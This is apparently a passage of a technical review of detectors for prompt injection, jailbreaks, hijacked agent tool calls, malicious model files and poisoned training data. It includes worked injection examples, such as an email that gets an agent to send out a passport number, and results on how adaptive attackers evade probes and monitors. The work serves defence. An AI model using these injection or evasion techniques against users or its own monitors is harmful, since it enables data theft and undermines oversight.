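Anthropic's Constitutional Classifiers, introduced in 2025, are language models trained to recognise forbidden requests and answers, using examples generated from a written set of rules. Later that year, Anthropic researchers showed that a probe followed by a larger classifier retained most of the larger classifier's accuracy while using little more compute than the probe alone. The January 2026 version, Constitutional Classifiers++, uses probes on activations from every layer of the model.

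*Prompt-Injection Probes Learn the Conversation, Not Just the Injection* (Kale and Vishwanath, 2026) reports that running probes before larger classifiers has cut costs more than tenfold in production systems. It also cites Anthropic's September 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5.5, which describes probes that check tool results for prompt injections across many of the company's products. Neither this paper nor the one by Kramár and colleagues gives a false positive rate for Anthropic's traffic.

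### Prompts from an unfamiliar source

The drop in AUROC that Fomin found when he held out whole datasets also occurred with activations from three other models. It ranged from 8 to 16.5 points on a 100-point scale and was largest for the two smallest models.

An overall AUROC also hides large differences between datasets. On one dataset with equal numbers of malicious and harmless prompts, accuracy was 94.5% when the training data included prompts from the same source and 69.1% when it did not. On another, excluding same-source prompts lowered accuracy by only 1.2 points. A probe on Llama 3.1 8B caught 98.9% of the attacks in InjecAgent, a collection of injections in tool results, while a probe on a 2-billion-parameter Qwen model caught none. The usual test did not reveal this difference, because both probes had nearly perfect results on it.

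Fomin tried seven standard fixes, and none closed the gap. One was to find and remove the activation patterns that reveal which dataset a prompt came from. This raised accuracy on one set of injections by 21 points but lowered it on InjecAgent by 34, probably because some of the patterns also help to identify attacks.

Other kinds of detector can fail on unfamiliar data too. Fomin tested two text classifiers built to detect prompt injection. One, from ProtectAI, flagged 4.2% of harmless prompts but caught only 8% of indirect injections. The other, from Deepset, caught 99.8% of attacks but also flagged 82.4% of harmless prompts, so its detection rate alone would be misleading.

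### Position and length as clues

Holding out a dataset does not help if every dataset contains the same misleading clue. Kale and Vishwanath found such a clue in AgentDojo, a benchmark that tests agents in simulated banking, office, Slack and travel applications. They recorded about 23,000 sessions for each of six open models with 8 to 31 billion parameters.

The usual way to train a probe on these sessions is to label each moment just before the agent acts as "attack" if the agent has just read an injection and "harmless" otherwise. Every session in the usual training data contains an attack, so the harmless moments come from before or after the injection. Attack moments therefore differ from harmless ones in when they occur and in how much text the agent has just read.

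Kale and Vishwanath measured how much these differences reveal by training a simple classifier on seven numbers, four for position in the conversation and three for text lengths. It had no access to the words or the activations, yet its AUROC was 0.96 to 0.98 in applications that appeared in the training data and 0.91 to 0.96 in new ones. Probes trained in the usual way scored 0.97 to 1.00. A near-perfect score on this test is therefore very weak evidence that a probe detects injections.

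Harder tests then compared attacks with two kinds of harmless case. A "clean twin" is the same moment in a session with the same task but no injection. A "look-alike" keeps the attack's formatting but replaces the attacker's request with a harmless notice. Against the clean twins, the seven-number classifier's AUROC dropped to between 0.65 and 0.75. The usual probes still ranked attacks above their twins fairly well, with a median AUROC of 0.87, so they had learned something about injections. But at the default threshold of 0.5, they flagged most of the harmless cases.

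The remedy was to add clean twins and look-alikes to the training data as matched negatives, which are harmless examples that share the attack's misleading features. The improved probe also used a slightly different training method, and its training data included attacks without their usual formatting. The table gives medians over the six models. The last column covers attacks the agent obeyed, with the threshold set to flag 1% of normal tool results in the training applications. The other columns use the default threshold.

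| Probe and setting | Clean twins flagged | Look-alikes flagged | Harmless instructions flagged | Unformatted attacks caught | Successful attacks caught |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Usual probe, familiar applications | 80% | 98% | 90% | 98% | 79% |
| Matched negatives, familiar applications | 17% | 11% | 33% | 96% | 95% |
| Usual probe, new applications | 70% | 94% | 82% | 95% | 80% |
| Matched negatives, new applications | 6% | 10% | 15% | 58% | 82% |

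The "harmless instructions" are sentences addressed to people, such as a request to bring a laptop to a workshop, and none of the probes was trained on them. Real emails contain many such sentences, so even the improved false-alarm rate of 15% to 33% would be a nuisance.

In familiar applications, the matched negatives sharply cut false alarms with almost no loss of detection. Most of the increase from 79% to 95% in the last column came from the new training method, which reached 91% without matched negatives. In new applications, the matched negatives again cut false alarms, but the probe missed many more unformatted attacks at the default threshold.

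The benefit also depends on the threshold. At the default setting in familiar applications, the usual probe would send 315,000 of every million tool results to a second check, and the improved one 74,000. At one second per check, that is 88 hours of computing versus 21. But when Kale and Vishwanath set the threshold to flag 1% of each new application's normal traffic, the usual probe caught 87% of successful attacks and the improved one only 74%. Such a strict threshold already avoids flagging most clean twins, so the matched negatives have fewer false alarms to prevent.

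The same training data improved a text classifier that used only word counts. In familiar applications, the share of look-alikes it flagged fell from 81% to 4%. In new applications, it caught 87% of successful attacks with a threshold based on local traffic, more than the improved probe caught. With a threshold carried over from the training applications, it caught 38%, compared with 82% for the probe. An operator who can collect normal traffic before launch may therefore not need activations, at least for attacks like those in AgentDojo. AgentDojo uses the same attacker accounts throughout each application, which may have made detection in familiar applications too easy.

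### Attacks designed to evade the detector

None of the tests so far involves an attacker who adjusts prompts in response to the detector. Nasr and colleagues, whose adaptive attacks bypassed twelve defences in 2025, argue that tests with fixed attacks overstate how robust a defence is. Kramár and colleagues acknowledge that their own methods do not significantly reduce the success of adaptive attacks, and say that doing so may be impossible. Even against publicly known jailbreaks in their main test, nearly every detector missed more than 1% of the prompts.

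In *Where Do LLMs Decide to Break the Rules?*, Wen, Liu and colleagues (2026) measured the effect of an informed attacker on one probe. To choose the probe's layer, they took cases in which Qwen3-4B, a 4-billion-parameter model, followed an injected instruction, and replaced its activations at a single layer with the average from cases in which it had not. This seldom changed the outcome in the first half of the network, but at layer 24 of 36 it stopped the model from following the injection in about 90% of cases.

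Layer 24 also gave the best detection of the three layers compared. On a test set of attacks and harmless questions with similar vocabulary, the layer-24 probe had an AUROC of 0.993, compared with 0.888 for a probe on the first layer and 0.709 for ProtectAI's text classifier. The layer-24 probe caught all of the attacks in which digits replaced some of the letters, while the first-layer probe caught only 13% of them.

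The probe was a much weaker defence against an attacker with full access to both it and the model. Its detection rate fell from 100% to 48% at a threshold set for 5% false positives, and the model still obeyed the altered injections. The attack succeeded because the probe's score depends on activations, and different wordings can produce the same behaviour with different activations. The detection rate of ProtectAI's classifier fell only from 62.5% to 60%. Using both detectors might therefore help, but Wen and colleagues did not test an attacker who tried to evade both.

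A detector can also combine information from many layers, which may make it harder to evade. *Defending Jailbreak Attacks on Large Language Models via Manifold Trajectory Kinetics* (Zhang, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) compares a new prompt's activations at each layer with those of a fixed set of harmless prompts and records which are closest. According to the paper, a harmless prompt stays close to other harmless prompts throughout, while a jailbreak starts near malicious ones and moves towards harmless ones in later layers. An outlier detector trained only on harmless prompts flags prompts whose pattern of closest matches across layers is unusual.

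On Llama 2 7B, the method caught 95% of jailbreaks and wrongly flagged 5% of ordinary prompts. It wrongly flagged 2% of prompts that only sound dangerous, such as a question about making a bomb-shaped cake. Against an informed attacker, it still caught 85% of attacks on another model, Vicuna 7B. Similar attacks reduced the detection rate of HiddenDetect, an earlier method based on activations, to almost zero. Zhang and colleagues calculate that 78% of attacks on Llama 2 and 90% on Vicuna both jailbroke the model and escaped HiddenDetect.

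The 85% figure is encouraging but provisional. Llama 2 and Vicuna date from 2023, and the detector's inventors also designed the attack on it, as happened with many earlier defences that later failed.

### Can a fixed set of guardrails be robust?

*Robust AI Security and Alignment* (Vassilev, 2026) makes the stronger claim that no defence of this kind can be fully robust. Its proof is based on Gödel's incompleteness theorem, that no fixed set of mathematical rules can prove every mathematical truth. NIST, where Vassilev works, announced the article in June 2026 and described its result as showing that a fixed set of guardrails (rules, filters or classifiers that decide which prompts to block) is not universally robust against adaptive prompts.

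The proof starts from the observation that there are infinitely many forbidden prompts, because anyone can lengthen one by adding harmless text. It then goes as follows:

1. Choose a large number *n*. Only finitely many computer programs are *n* bits long or shorter, and each prints at most one prompt. Some forbidden prompt *x* must therefore need a program longer than *n* bits to print it.
2. Suppose the guardrail could verify a proof of that fact about *x*.
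3. Someone could then write a program that searches through all forbidden prompts and all possible proofs until the guardrail accepts one, and prints the corresponding prompt.
4. This program is short. Apart from a fixed part, it needs to contain only the number *n*, and a number as large as a million takes just 20 bits. For large enough *n*, the program is shorter than *n* bits and yet prints *x*, which contradicts step 1.

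The guardrail can therefore never verify that *x* needs a program longer than *n* bits. This is a version of a theorem by Gregory Chaitin, and the reasoning is sound if the guardrail accepts only valid proofs.

But the conclusion about security does not follow. The guardrail cannot verify a fact about the length of the shortest program that prints *x*, but it does not need to know that length to block *x*. The theorem applies even to a guardrail that blocks every prompt, which is useless but perfectly robust. The search in step 3 also requires a program that can identify the forbidden prompts, which guardrails supposedly cannot do.

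Vassilev also gives a version for real systems, which limit prompt length. The number of possible prompts is then finite, so a complete list of the forbidden ones exists in principle. He says nobody could compile it, but that obstacle is practical rather than logical. His proof for this version has two cases. In one of them, the statement that the guardrail fails to verify is false, so failing to verify it is not a weakness.

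*No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) proves a related, more precise limit for computer programs. It considers a gatekeeper that must decide from a program's code whether the program will ever perform a forbidden action. Suppose a program checks even numbers one by one and performs the action only if it finds one above 2 that is not the sum of two primes. This program is safe only if Goldbach's conjecture, an unsolved problem, is true. The theorem is that no gatekeeper relying on checkable evidence can approve every safe program and no unsafe one.

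A gatekeeper can still avoid approving any unsafe program by rejecting every program it cannot prove safe, but it will then reject some safe ones too. The theorem therefore rules out catching every unsafe program without false alarms, but not robustness by itself. It describes the worst case and gives no probability of harm. In simulations with 2.2 million random programs, Pérez-Acle found that the difficulty comes from programs built to defeat the gatekeeper, not from typical ones. The theorem applies to programs that can run forever, not to prompts, whose harmfulness depends on meaning and context.

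Neither proof gives a detection rate. Both would hold whether a detector caught 99.9% of the attacks people attempt or half of them. Experiments such as those of Nasr and colleagues are better evidence that guardrails are fallible.

Vassilev's practical advice is sensible even without the proof. He recommends that operators constantly search for new attacks, update their guardrails in response, and prepare to limit the damage when an attack succeeds. He aims to make finding a new attack take more resources than attackers have. The detection rates in these studies do not measure progress towards that aim, because they are based on how many attacks succeed and not on how much effort it takes to find them.

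## Scoring the actions of AI agents

A detector that scores only text may miss a prompt injection worded like ordinary office text. *AttriGuard* (He, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) gives an example that got past PromptArmor, a defence in which a language model removes injected instructions from the agent's input. The injection presented sending a company's Slack messages to an outside website as a routine audit step after a new colleague joins. The agent's attempt to send the messages is easier to recognise as an attack, because nothing the user asked for requires it.

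### One hijacked session

Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise today's unread email. The trace then continues with four entries:

1. The agent calls `read_unread_emails`.
2. The tool returns three emails. One of them, from an outside sender, contains a request to forward the user's passport number to an unfamiliar address.
3. The agent calls `send_email` with that address and the passport number.
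4. The agent gives the user an accurate summary of the three emails.

The user sees a correct answer and has no reason to complain. The evidence is in entry 3, because the agent does not need to send anything to write a summary. A detector can still prevent the theft if it scores this call before the software carries it out.

If the user had also asked the agent to email the summary to a colleague, the task would need `send_email`, and the attacker would only have to change the recipient. He and colleagues note that such attacks are generally harder to stop because restricting the agent's tools does not help.

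Most of the figures below come from AgentDojo, the set of simulated applications used to test the probes in the previous section. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) combines 97 user tasks with attackers' goals to make 629 test cases. After each test, ordinary code checks the simulated inbox or bank account to see whether the attack worked, because an injection might also hijack a judge model.

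Studies that use AgentDojo usually report the attack success rate and the share of harmless tasks the agent completes, but rarely the detector's true and false positive rates. A detector that blocks necessary tool calls lowers the share of completed tasks, so the drop is a rough substitute for a false positive rate.

The attack success rate depends on the agent as well as the detector. In the original 2024 AgentDojo tests, attacks succeeded in just under 25% of cases against the best agents of the time. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) found that AgentDojo's standard attack succeeded only 0.3% of the time against Claude Haiku 4.5 with no defence. A near-zero rate on a recent model may therefore not be due to the detector at all.

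### Checking each call against the task

The most direct score measures whether a call fits the user's request. Its inputs are the request, the descriptions of the available tools and the proposed call:

1. Before the agent reads any outside text, a language model reads the request and lists the tools the task should need.
2. Software compares each call the agent proposes with the list.
3. If the tool is not on the list, the software blocks the call.

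For the email summary, the list would contain `read_unread_emails` but not `send_email`, so the software would block entry 3. This adds only one model call per task.

*MELON* (Zhu, Yang and colleagues, 2025) tested a simple filter of this kind with GPT-4o, a 2024 model. The filter cut the success rate of the strongest of four attacks from 51.0% to 6.5%, but the share of harmless tasks completed also fell, from 80.4% to 66.0%. With another model, o3-mini, the filter removed so many tools that the agent completed only 4% of harmless tasks, compared with 58% without it.

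Later systems use more detailed plans. DRIFT predicts a course of action from the request and checks the agent's actions against it, while Progent writes rules that allow or deny particular calls. On GPT-4o-mini, the standard attack succeeded against DRIFT 2.6% of the time, and attacks that Ma and colleagues adapted by trial and error succeeded 6.4%. The same method raised attack success against PIGuard, a text classifier, from 0% to 28%. But DRIFT reduced the share of harmless tasks completed by 18 percentage points on GPT-4o-mini and 25 on Claude Haiku 4.5, while Progent reduced it by at most 7.

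These systems typically fail when the right action depends on something the agent has not yet read. *ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) tested them on AgentDyn, a newer benchmark with more open-ended tasks. GPT-4o-mini completed 46.7% of harmless tasks without a defence, 18.3% with DRIFT and 6.7% with Progent, although Progent had reduced task completion only slightly on AgentDojo.

Vague requests are the most extreme case of this problem. A user may ask an agent to do everything on a to-do list at some web address, so the page's contents entirely determine what the agent does. In the *AutoDojo* experiments, the standard attack on GPT-4o-mini with no defence succeeded 87.5% of the time on such requests and at most 63.9% of the time on more precise ones. DRIFT and Progent kept attack success at or below 11% for every kind of request, largely because their plans for vague requests often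 limit the agent to read-only tools. This restriction also stops the agent from doing most of what is on the list.

A less rigid score could account for how much damage a tool call might do, since an unexpected payment matters much more than an unexpected look at a calendar. *Prompt Injection Detection for Email Agents Through Attack Chain Modeling* (2026) describes a framework that assesses both an action's risk and its consistency with the user's intent.

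### Running the step again without the user's request

Re-execution tests rerun the agent's latest step with part of the input changed. MELON, one such test, hides the user's request and keeps the outside text. If the agent still proposes the same tool call, the outside text probably caused it.

1. The agent proposes a tool call *c*.
2. The software gives the same model all the tool results so far, but replaces the user's request with a neutral instruction to summarise the content and carry out any instructions in it.
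3. It stores every tool call *h* that the model makes in this second run, including those from earlier steps.
4. An embedding model, which turns text into a list of numbers that reflects its meaning, converts a description of each call into a list *φ*.
5. The software stops the agent if the score exceeds 0.8, where

score(*c*) = max over *h* of *φ(c)* · *φ(h)* / (|*φ(c)*| |*φ(h)*|).

In the email example, the second run omits the user's request but keeps the attacker's email. The model again calls `send_email` with the attacker's address, so the two calls match and the software raises an alarm. An email to a colleague named only by the user would have no match. Storing the earlier calls helps because a hijacked agent may finish the user's task before starting the attacker's.

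MELON roughly doubles the number of model calls, though the two runs can be done in parallel. With GPT-4o, it reduced the success rate of the strongest attack from 51.0% to 1.0%. Its false positive rate was 9.3%, or nine of the 97 harmless tasks. All nine asked the agent to follow instructions from an outside source, such as an online to-do list. Zhu and colleagues argue that these alarms point to real security risks, but the agent would still be unable to do the task for a user who wrote the list. The agent completed 12 fewer tasks with MELON, so the nine false alarms do not explain the whole loss.

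In 73% of 66 attacks that MELON missed on three models, the attacker's goal needed no tool call, because the agent only had to give the user a message, such as a recommendation to buy an expensive product. In most of the others, the two runs differed, for example when the second run looked up information that the first already had.

Zhu and colleagues call the defence provable because of a bound on its errors. If the software repeats the test with *n* neutral instructions and averages the similarities, the chance of missing an attack is at most

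exp(−2*n*(*μ* − *θ*)²),

where *μ* is the expected similarity for attacks and *θ* the threshold. With 100 instructions, an expected similarity of 0.7 and a threshold of 0.5, this is e⁻⁸, or about 0.03%. (The paper gives 0.018%.) But the bound applies only if *μ* is above the threshold, and an adaptive attacker looks for injections that push it below. A hundred instructions would also mean a hundred extra runs at every step.

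### Running the step again with weaker outside text

AttriGuard makes the opposite change. It keeps the user's request, weakens the outside text, and raises an alarm if the proposed call disappears. The quantity it tries to estimate is the control effect of the outside text on a call *c*,

CE(*c*) = ln *p(c)* − ln *p₀(c)*,

where *p(c)* is the probability that the agent makes the call after reading the original text, and *p₀(c)* is the probability when the text can still supply facts but cannot steer the agent. If weakening the emails reduces the probability of the `send_email` call from 0.9 to 0.01, the control effect is 4.5. If the probability of a legitimate call goes from 0.98 to 0.97, the effect is only 0.01.

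Commercial services do not reveal these probabilities, so AttriGuard checks whether the call reappears:

1. A language model rewrites the tool results. It turns code-like structures into plain sentences and commands into reports, so that "You should send the report" becomes a statement that the text says someone should send it.
2. The agent repeats its latest step with the rewritten results, while its earlier actions stay the same.
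3. If the second run does not call the same tool, the software blocks the original call.
4. If it calls the same tool with the same arguments, the original call goes ahead. If the arguments differ, a judge model decides whether the original call fits the user's task.

The agent still works from the original text, because the rewritten version may have lost details that the task needs. On Gemini 2.5 Flash, the average time per test case rose from 11.5 seconds to 32.4 seconds, compared with 16.6 seconds for MELON.

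AttriGuard stopped all the standard attacks on AgentDojo with four models. He and colleagues removed 62 of the 944 cases before testing because the attacker only wanted the agent to write something or the user had left the decision to outside text. MELON had trouble with these kinds of cases. Most agents completed about as many harmless tasks as before, but Llama 3.3 70B completed roughly 20% fewer of the long travel tasks because its two runs often differed even without an attack.

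He and colleagues then gave an adaptive attacker full knowledge of each defence and 200 attempts at each of 61 cases. The table shows attack success rates on Gemini 2.5 Flash.

| Defence | What it examines | Standard attack | Adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | Outside text | 4.9% | 52.5% |
| PromptArmor | Outside text | 0% | 29.5% |
| MELON | Calls, with the user's request hidden | 0% | 82.0% |
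| AttriGuard | Calls, with the outside text weakened | 0% | 6.6% |

MELON had the worst result of the four, so scoring actions does not by itself protect against an informed attacker. AttriGuard's own developers measured its 6.6%, which represents only four successful attacks.

### Influence and permission

Both re-execution tests measure what influenced a call, not whether the user authorised it. *Influence Is Not Authority* (Ahad, Hossain and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to send money to Alice without giving her account number. The agent has to look the number up with a tool, so outside text influences the payment even though the payment is what the user wanted.

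To measure how much a value's source affects the score, they built 24 cases in which the action stayed the same and only the source of one value changed, from the user's request to a legitimate tool. They scored each action by removing each source in turn and measuring how much support the action lost. Changing the value's source made the action look more like an attack in all 24 cases. On average, it shifted the score further than replacing the authorised action with an unauthorised one, such as paying someone other than Alice.

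In constructed cases of this kind, AttriGuard blocked 47.1% of authorised actions and 36.3% of matching unauthorised ones, a difference that could be due to chance. Its judge blocked a larger share of the unauthorised actions that reached it, but 57.5% of unauthorised actions passed automatically before that step, compared with 29.2% of authorised ones. AttriGuard allowed every harmless run in the study, so the 47.1% figure does not estimate its false positive rate in ordinary use. In a separate live test on 14 tasks, it cut the rate of one unauthorised outcome from 24.3% to 2.9%.

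ROPE checks where each sensitive value came from instead of estimating influence. A language model receives only trusted information, mainly the user's request, and selects which sources may supply a value such as the account number for a payment. It might allow the user's own transaction records. Before the payment, ordinary code checks that the number appears in one of those sources. A number that appears only in an attacker's email fails this check, however the email is worded.

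On AgentDyn, ROPE reduced attack success on GPT-4o-mini from 49.6% to 0.3%, and the agent completed 36.7% of harmless tasks, twice as many as with DRIFT. ROPE protects only against harm done through tool calls, and it depends on correct rules and on sources that an attacker cannot forge. *AutoDojo* also reports good results for ROPE, but four of ROPE's five authors worked on that study too.

### Comparing a session with past sessions

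A company that runs the same agent every day can also score how unusual a sequence of calls is. The only input is the log of past sessions. The software counts how often each call followed each other call, and scores a session of *n* calls as

−(1/*n*) Σᵢ ln *P(cᵢ | cᵢ₋₁)*,

where *P(cᵢ | cᵢ₋₁)* is the share of past cases in which call *cᵢ* came directly after the previous one. If the agent sent an email after reading the inbox in 10 of 1,000 past sessions, that step contributes −ln 0.01, or 4.6. If it did so in 300, because many users ask it to send replies, the same step contributes only 1.2. The calculation costs almost nothing, as it needs no further model calls.

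A user's first attempt at a new kind of task can look as unusual as an attack, and an attack that needs only a common sequence of tool calls gets a low score. He and colleagues compare 13 other defences and *AutoDojo* compares ten, but neither comparison includes a detector based on past tool calls.

This approach can fail badly on unfamiliar data. DynaHug, a related detector, learns which system calls software makes when it loads ordinary model files, and flags files that depart from this pattern. In *I Don't Care How You Hide It, I Care What You Do*, Ali and Case (2026) tested DynaHug on 84 malicious files and 252 harmless ones. It flagged all 336, so its detection rate and false positive rate were both 100%. Ali and Case, who developed a competing detector, attribute this to DynaHug's training data, which came only from models that generate text.

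### A model that reads the whole trace

A language model can judge a complete session from the user's request, the tool calls, their results and the final outcome. This can reveal harm that builds up over several steps, but long traces take a lot of compute to process. A model that sees only the trace also lacks information about the user's permissions.

Ahad and colleagues tested AgentWatcher, a judge that applies written rules to the text that influenced an action. It reduced attack success from 16% to 0% on 200 matched inputs, but the share of tasks completed fell from 60% to 28%. When outside text conflicted with the user's request, AgentWatcher flagged authorised and unauthorised actions alike.

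The best-documented field evidence comes from Snowflake, a company that sells data storage and analysis. In 2026 it published a review of 610 internal agent sessions that its own detector had flagged:

| Outcome of the review | Sessions | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Confirmed detection | 21 | 3.4% |
| Possible detection | 2 | 0.3% |
| More context needed | 26 | 4.3% |
| Authorised work | 561 | 92.0% |

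The precision was about 3%, and would be 8% if every unresolved case were real. Most false alarms came from legitimate work that resembled an attack, such as security reviews and permission checks. Snowflake found that neither the type of action nor the model's confidence was a good substitute for knowing the context.

This is a vendor's own count, and Snowflake cautions that it does not measure accuracy in production. The detector also targets people who misuse an agent for cyberattacks, so the result is only indirect evidence about prompt injection. The number of missed cases is unknown because the review covered only flagged sessions.

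Another Snowflake post describes a cascade whose second, larger model also receives information such as the user's role and the authorised scope of the work. In about 6,000 sessions from staff who test security by attacking systems, the first stage flagged every participant, but the second issued no alerts once it took their permissions into account.

The system flagged three people based on about 12,000 traces from ordinary engineers. One case was real, in which an agent had shut down a process for every user of a shared workspace. Three other models also reviewed every trace, but Snowflake does not say how many missed cases they found. The company now processes about 18,000 traces a day and flags fewer than 0.2% of them, or at most 36.

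### Watching what a model file does

Zhang, Wang and colleagues (2026) argue in *LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring* that operators should expect attacks during normal operation and look for signs of them throughout an application. They model this monitoring on the software that security teams use to watch a company's computers. Signs of an attack in tool results include fields of an unexpected type or length, and instructions where a tool should return only data.

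System calls matter most when the attack is a program hidden in a model file. Developers often download models from public sites such as Hugging Face, and some file formats can run code as soon as software opens them. Most scanners search the file for suspicious functions without running it. ModelShield, Ali and Case's detector, runs the model in isolation and records what it does:

1. It attaches an identifier to each operation that loads or runs the model.
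2. A monitor in the operating system records every system call with the identifier of the operation that caused it, and passes the identifier on to any new process.
3. The software compares the resulting sequences with 195 patterns of malicious behaviour.

The second step separates the model's behaviour from the thousands of system calls that the surrounding software makes. The patterns require a harmful sequence of actions, so reading a private key does not raise an alarm by itself, but it does if the model then connects to an outside address and sends about as much data as it read.

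On the test set that DynaHug had flagged in full, ModelShield caught 47 of the 84 malicious files (56%) and flagged none of the 252 harmless ones. Because there were only 252 harmless files, this result can only rule out false positive rates above about 1.2%. Of the 37 malicious files it missed, 23 ran without doing anything harmful, and most of those only printed text. Nine needed missing software or a Windows computer, four were defective, and one contained no attack. PickleScan, which examines files without running them, caught 79 of the malicious files but flagged 16 harmless ones.

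Ali and Case also scanned 145,000 public models and found 41 malicious ones, all on Hugging Face. One gave its author remote control of any computer that loaded it, and users had downloaded it 108 times in three days. To check for malicious models they had missed, they ran other scanners on 10,000 of the models and checked the 565 flagged files by hand. ModelShield had caught five of the eight files that were malicious.

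The median analysis took 12.3 seconds, and 90% finished within 35.5 seconds. That is slower than the other scanners but fast enough to check a file before use. ModelShield can still miss code that waits for a particular input or date. It also cannot detect a backdoor learned from poisoned training data, because the planted behaviour is in the model's parameters and need not cause unusual system calls.

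## Scoring training examples by how the model learns them

A developer who suspects that someone has poisoned a training set can search it before releasing the model. At that stage, the developer has no bad output to trace to its source and doesn't know the trigger or what the backdoor does.

The usual approach is to train a model on all the suspect data and log how it responds to each training example. The developer scores the responses, removes the examples with the highest scores and trains a new model on the rest. This works only if the model learns poisoned examples differently from clean ones. Researchers have looked for that difference in the model's activations and in how quickly the loss on each example falls.

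The best-known methods date from 2018 to 2021 and were originally tested mainly on small image classifiers, so their detection rates are out of date.

### Activation clustering

Suppose an attacker adds photographs of stop signs with a yellow sticker to a training set and labels them "speed limit". The trained model gives these the same label as real speed-limit signs, but for a different reason: it recognises a stop sign with a sticker, not a number in a circle. Chen, Carvalho and colleagues (2018), in *Detecting Backdoor Attacks on Deep Neural Networks by Activation Clustering*, expected this difference to show in the activations. Their method has five steps:

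1. Train a classifier on the untrusted data.
2. Run every training example through it and record the activations of the last hidden layer.
3. Take the examples of one class and compress each one's activations to ten numbers.
4. Split the examples into two groups with k-means, an algorithm that puts each point in the group whose centre is nearest.
5. Decide whether either group is poison, then repeat for the other classes.

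Step 5 is necessary because k-means always produces two groups, even from a clean class. The simplest test is size, since a clean class tends to split fairly evenly while poison forms a smaller group. A second test is the silhouette score, which measures how well separated the groups are. The third test retrains the classifier without the suspect group and then runs it on that group. The new model should give most of the examples their original label if the group is clean, and label them as stop signs if it is poison. The test divides the number that get their original label by the number that get the most common other label, and a ratio below 1 indicates poison.

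The table shows the results for ten classes, each tested once clean and once poisoned.

| Test | Clean classes | Poisoned classes |
|---|---|---|
| Share of the class in the smaller group | 30% to 47% | 9% to 29% |
| Silhouette score | 0.07 to 0.11 | 0.09 to 0.33 |
| Ratio after retraining | 3.54 to 315.5 | 0 to 0.13 |

Only the third test shows a wide gap between clean and poisoned classes, but it takes the most compute because it requires training another model. It can be used to distinguish poison from a natural subgroup, such as sevens written with a crossbar, because a retrained model should still recognise most of those as sevens. A group of accidental labelling mistakes would look the same as poison, but the developer would want to remove those anyway.

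With 10% of each MNIST class poisoned, the clustering grouped 99.97% of the digits correctly, compared with 58.6% when it used raw pixels. It made no errors on American traffic signs with 15% or 33% of a class poisoned, or on film reviews with 10% of the negative class poisoned. It also got 99.9% right when Chen, Carvalho and colleagues merged the sevens, eights and nines into one class and poisoned it with three other digits.

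These are large shares of poison. On the traffic signs, the researchers couldn't plant a working backdoor with 10% or less, so the tests provide little evidence about attacks that need far fewer poisoned examples.

Once the developer has found the poisoned examples, removing the backdoor takes less computation than retraining from scratch. Correcting the labels on the poisoned digits and continuing to train removed it in 14 passes over those examples, while retraining from scratch took 80 passes over the whole dataset.

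Later tests were less favourable. *Backdoor Vulnerabilities in Normally Trained Deep Learning Models* (2022) compared silhouette scores for clean image sets and sets that included backdoored images. The two ranges overlapped, and many clean sets had high scores, so a threshold would have raised false alarms. *An Overview of Backdoor Attacks Against Deep Neural Networks and Possible Defences* (2021) reports that poisoned and clean activations separate poorly when the trigger is subtle, such as a single changed pixel in a CIFAR-10 image.

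### Spectral signatures

In *Spectral Signatures in Backdoor Attacks*, Tran, Li and Mądry (2018) scored each example individually rather than sorting examples into groups. They reasoned that a classifier amplifies any feature that strongly predicts a label, and a trigger predicts its label almost perfectly. The model's internal representations of the poisoned examples should therefore all shift in the same direction. If the shift is large enough, that direction is the one in which the class's representations vary most.

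For each class, the software computes the average activations *m* and subtracts them from the activations *a(xᵢ)* of every example. It then finds the direction *v*, of length 1, along which the centred activations vary most. The score is the squared projection on that direction:

score(*xᵢ*) = ((*a(xᵢ)* − *m*) · *v*)².

In the invented example below, a class contains six photographs, five clean and one poisoned, and each has two activations. The activations average 4 and 5, and their main direction is (0.8, 0.6).

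| Photograph | Activations | After centring | Projection | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean A | 1.8, 4.6 | −2.2, −0.4 | −2 | 4 |
| Clean B | 2.0, 6.0 | −2.0, 1.0 | −1 | 1 |
| Clean C | 5.0, 2.0 | 1.0, −3.0 | −1 | 1 |
| Clean D | 3.4, 5.8 | −0.6, 0.8 | 0 | 0 |
| Clean E | 3.8, 3.6 | −0.2, −1.4 | −1 | 1 |
| Poisoned | 8.0, 8.0 | 4.0, 3.0 | 5 | 25 |

The poisoned photograph's projection is 4 × 0.8 + 3 × 0.6 = 5. Photograph C is the most unusual clean photograph, but it scores only 1 because it differs from the average in another direction. A rare but clean example can therefore be kept, as long as rare examples don't all differ in the same way.

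The software removes the highest-scoring examples from every class, 1.5 times as many as the defender thinks an attacker could have added. In the example, the defender assumes the attacker added at most one photograph, so the software removes one or two, depending on how it rounds 1.5. If it removes two, the second is clean photograph A.

Tran and colleagues prove when this must work. Let *ε* be the poisoned share of the class, *μ* and *μ′* the average activations of its clean and poisoned examples, and *σ*² an upper limit on how much either group varies in any direction. If

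‖*μ* − *μ′*‖² ≥ 6*σ*²/*ε*,

then some threshold on the projection misclassifies less than a fraction *ε* of each group. With 10% poison, the averages must be at least 7.7*σ* apart, and with 0.1% they must be 77*σ* apart. The condition is sufficient but not necessary, so detection can succeed at smaller distances. But it shows why rare poison is harder to find, since a few examples have little influence on the main direction of variation.

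The tests used CIFAR-10, which has 5,000 training images per class, with triggers as small as one pixel. In the main results, adding 250 poisoned images to a class (5%) produced backdoors that worked 74% to 99.8% of the time. One round of removal left 0 to 57 of those 250 images, and at most seven when 500 (10%) had been added. After retraining, the backdoor's success rate was within one percentage point of the error rate of a classifier trained on clean data. The 57 images left in the worst case were too few to keep the backdoor working, though that backdoor was also the weakest before removal.

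The method also worked on a more varied class. When the researchers merged cats and dogs into a "pets" class and added poisoned cars, the method removed every poisoned image.

The software also removed many clean images. If the defender assumes at most 250 poisoned images per class, the software removes 375 from each of the ten classes, or 3,750 in total. At least 3,500 of these are clean (7% of the clean data), so the precision is at most 6.7%.

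*Hidden Trigger Backdoor Attacks* (2019) tested a detector on poisoned images in which the trigger is not visible. Although the test specified which class to search, and the detector flagged 135 of 800 images, it found none of the 100 poisoned ones for most pairs of classes and about half for one pair. Researchers have since applied this detection method to models of program code. *Optimizing Spectral Signature in Code Backdoor Detection* (2025) reports attacks on such models that always succeeded with only 1% of the data poisoned.

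### How quickly the model learns an example

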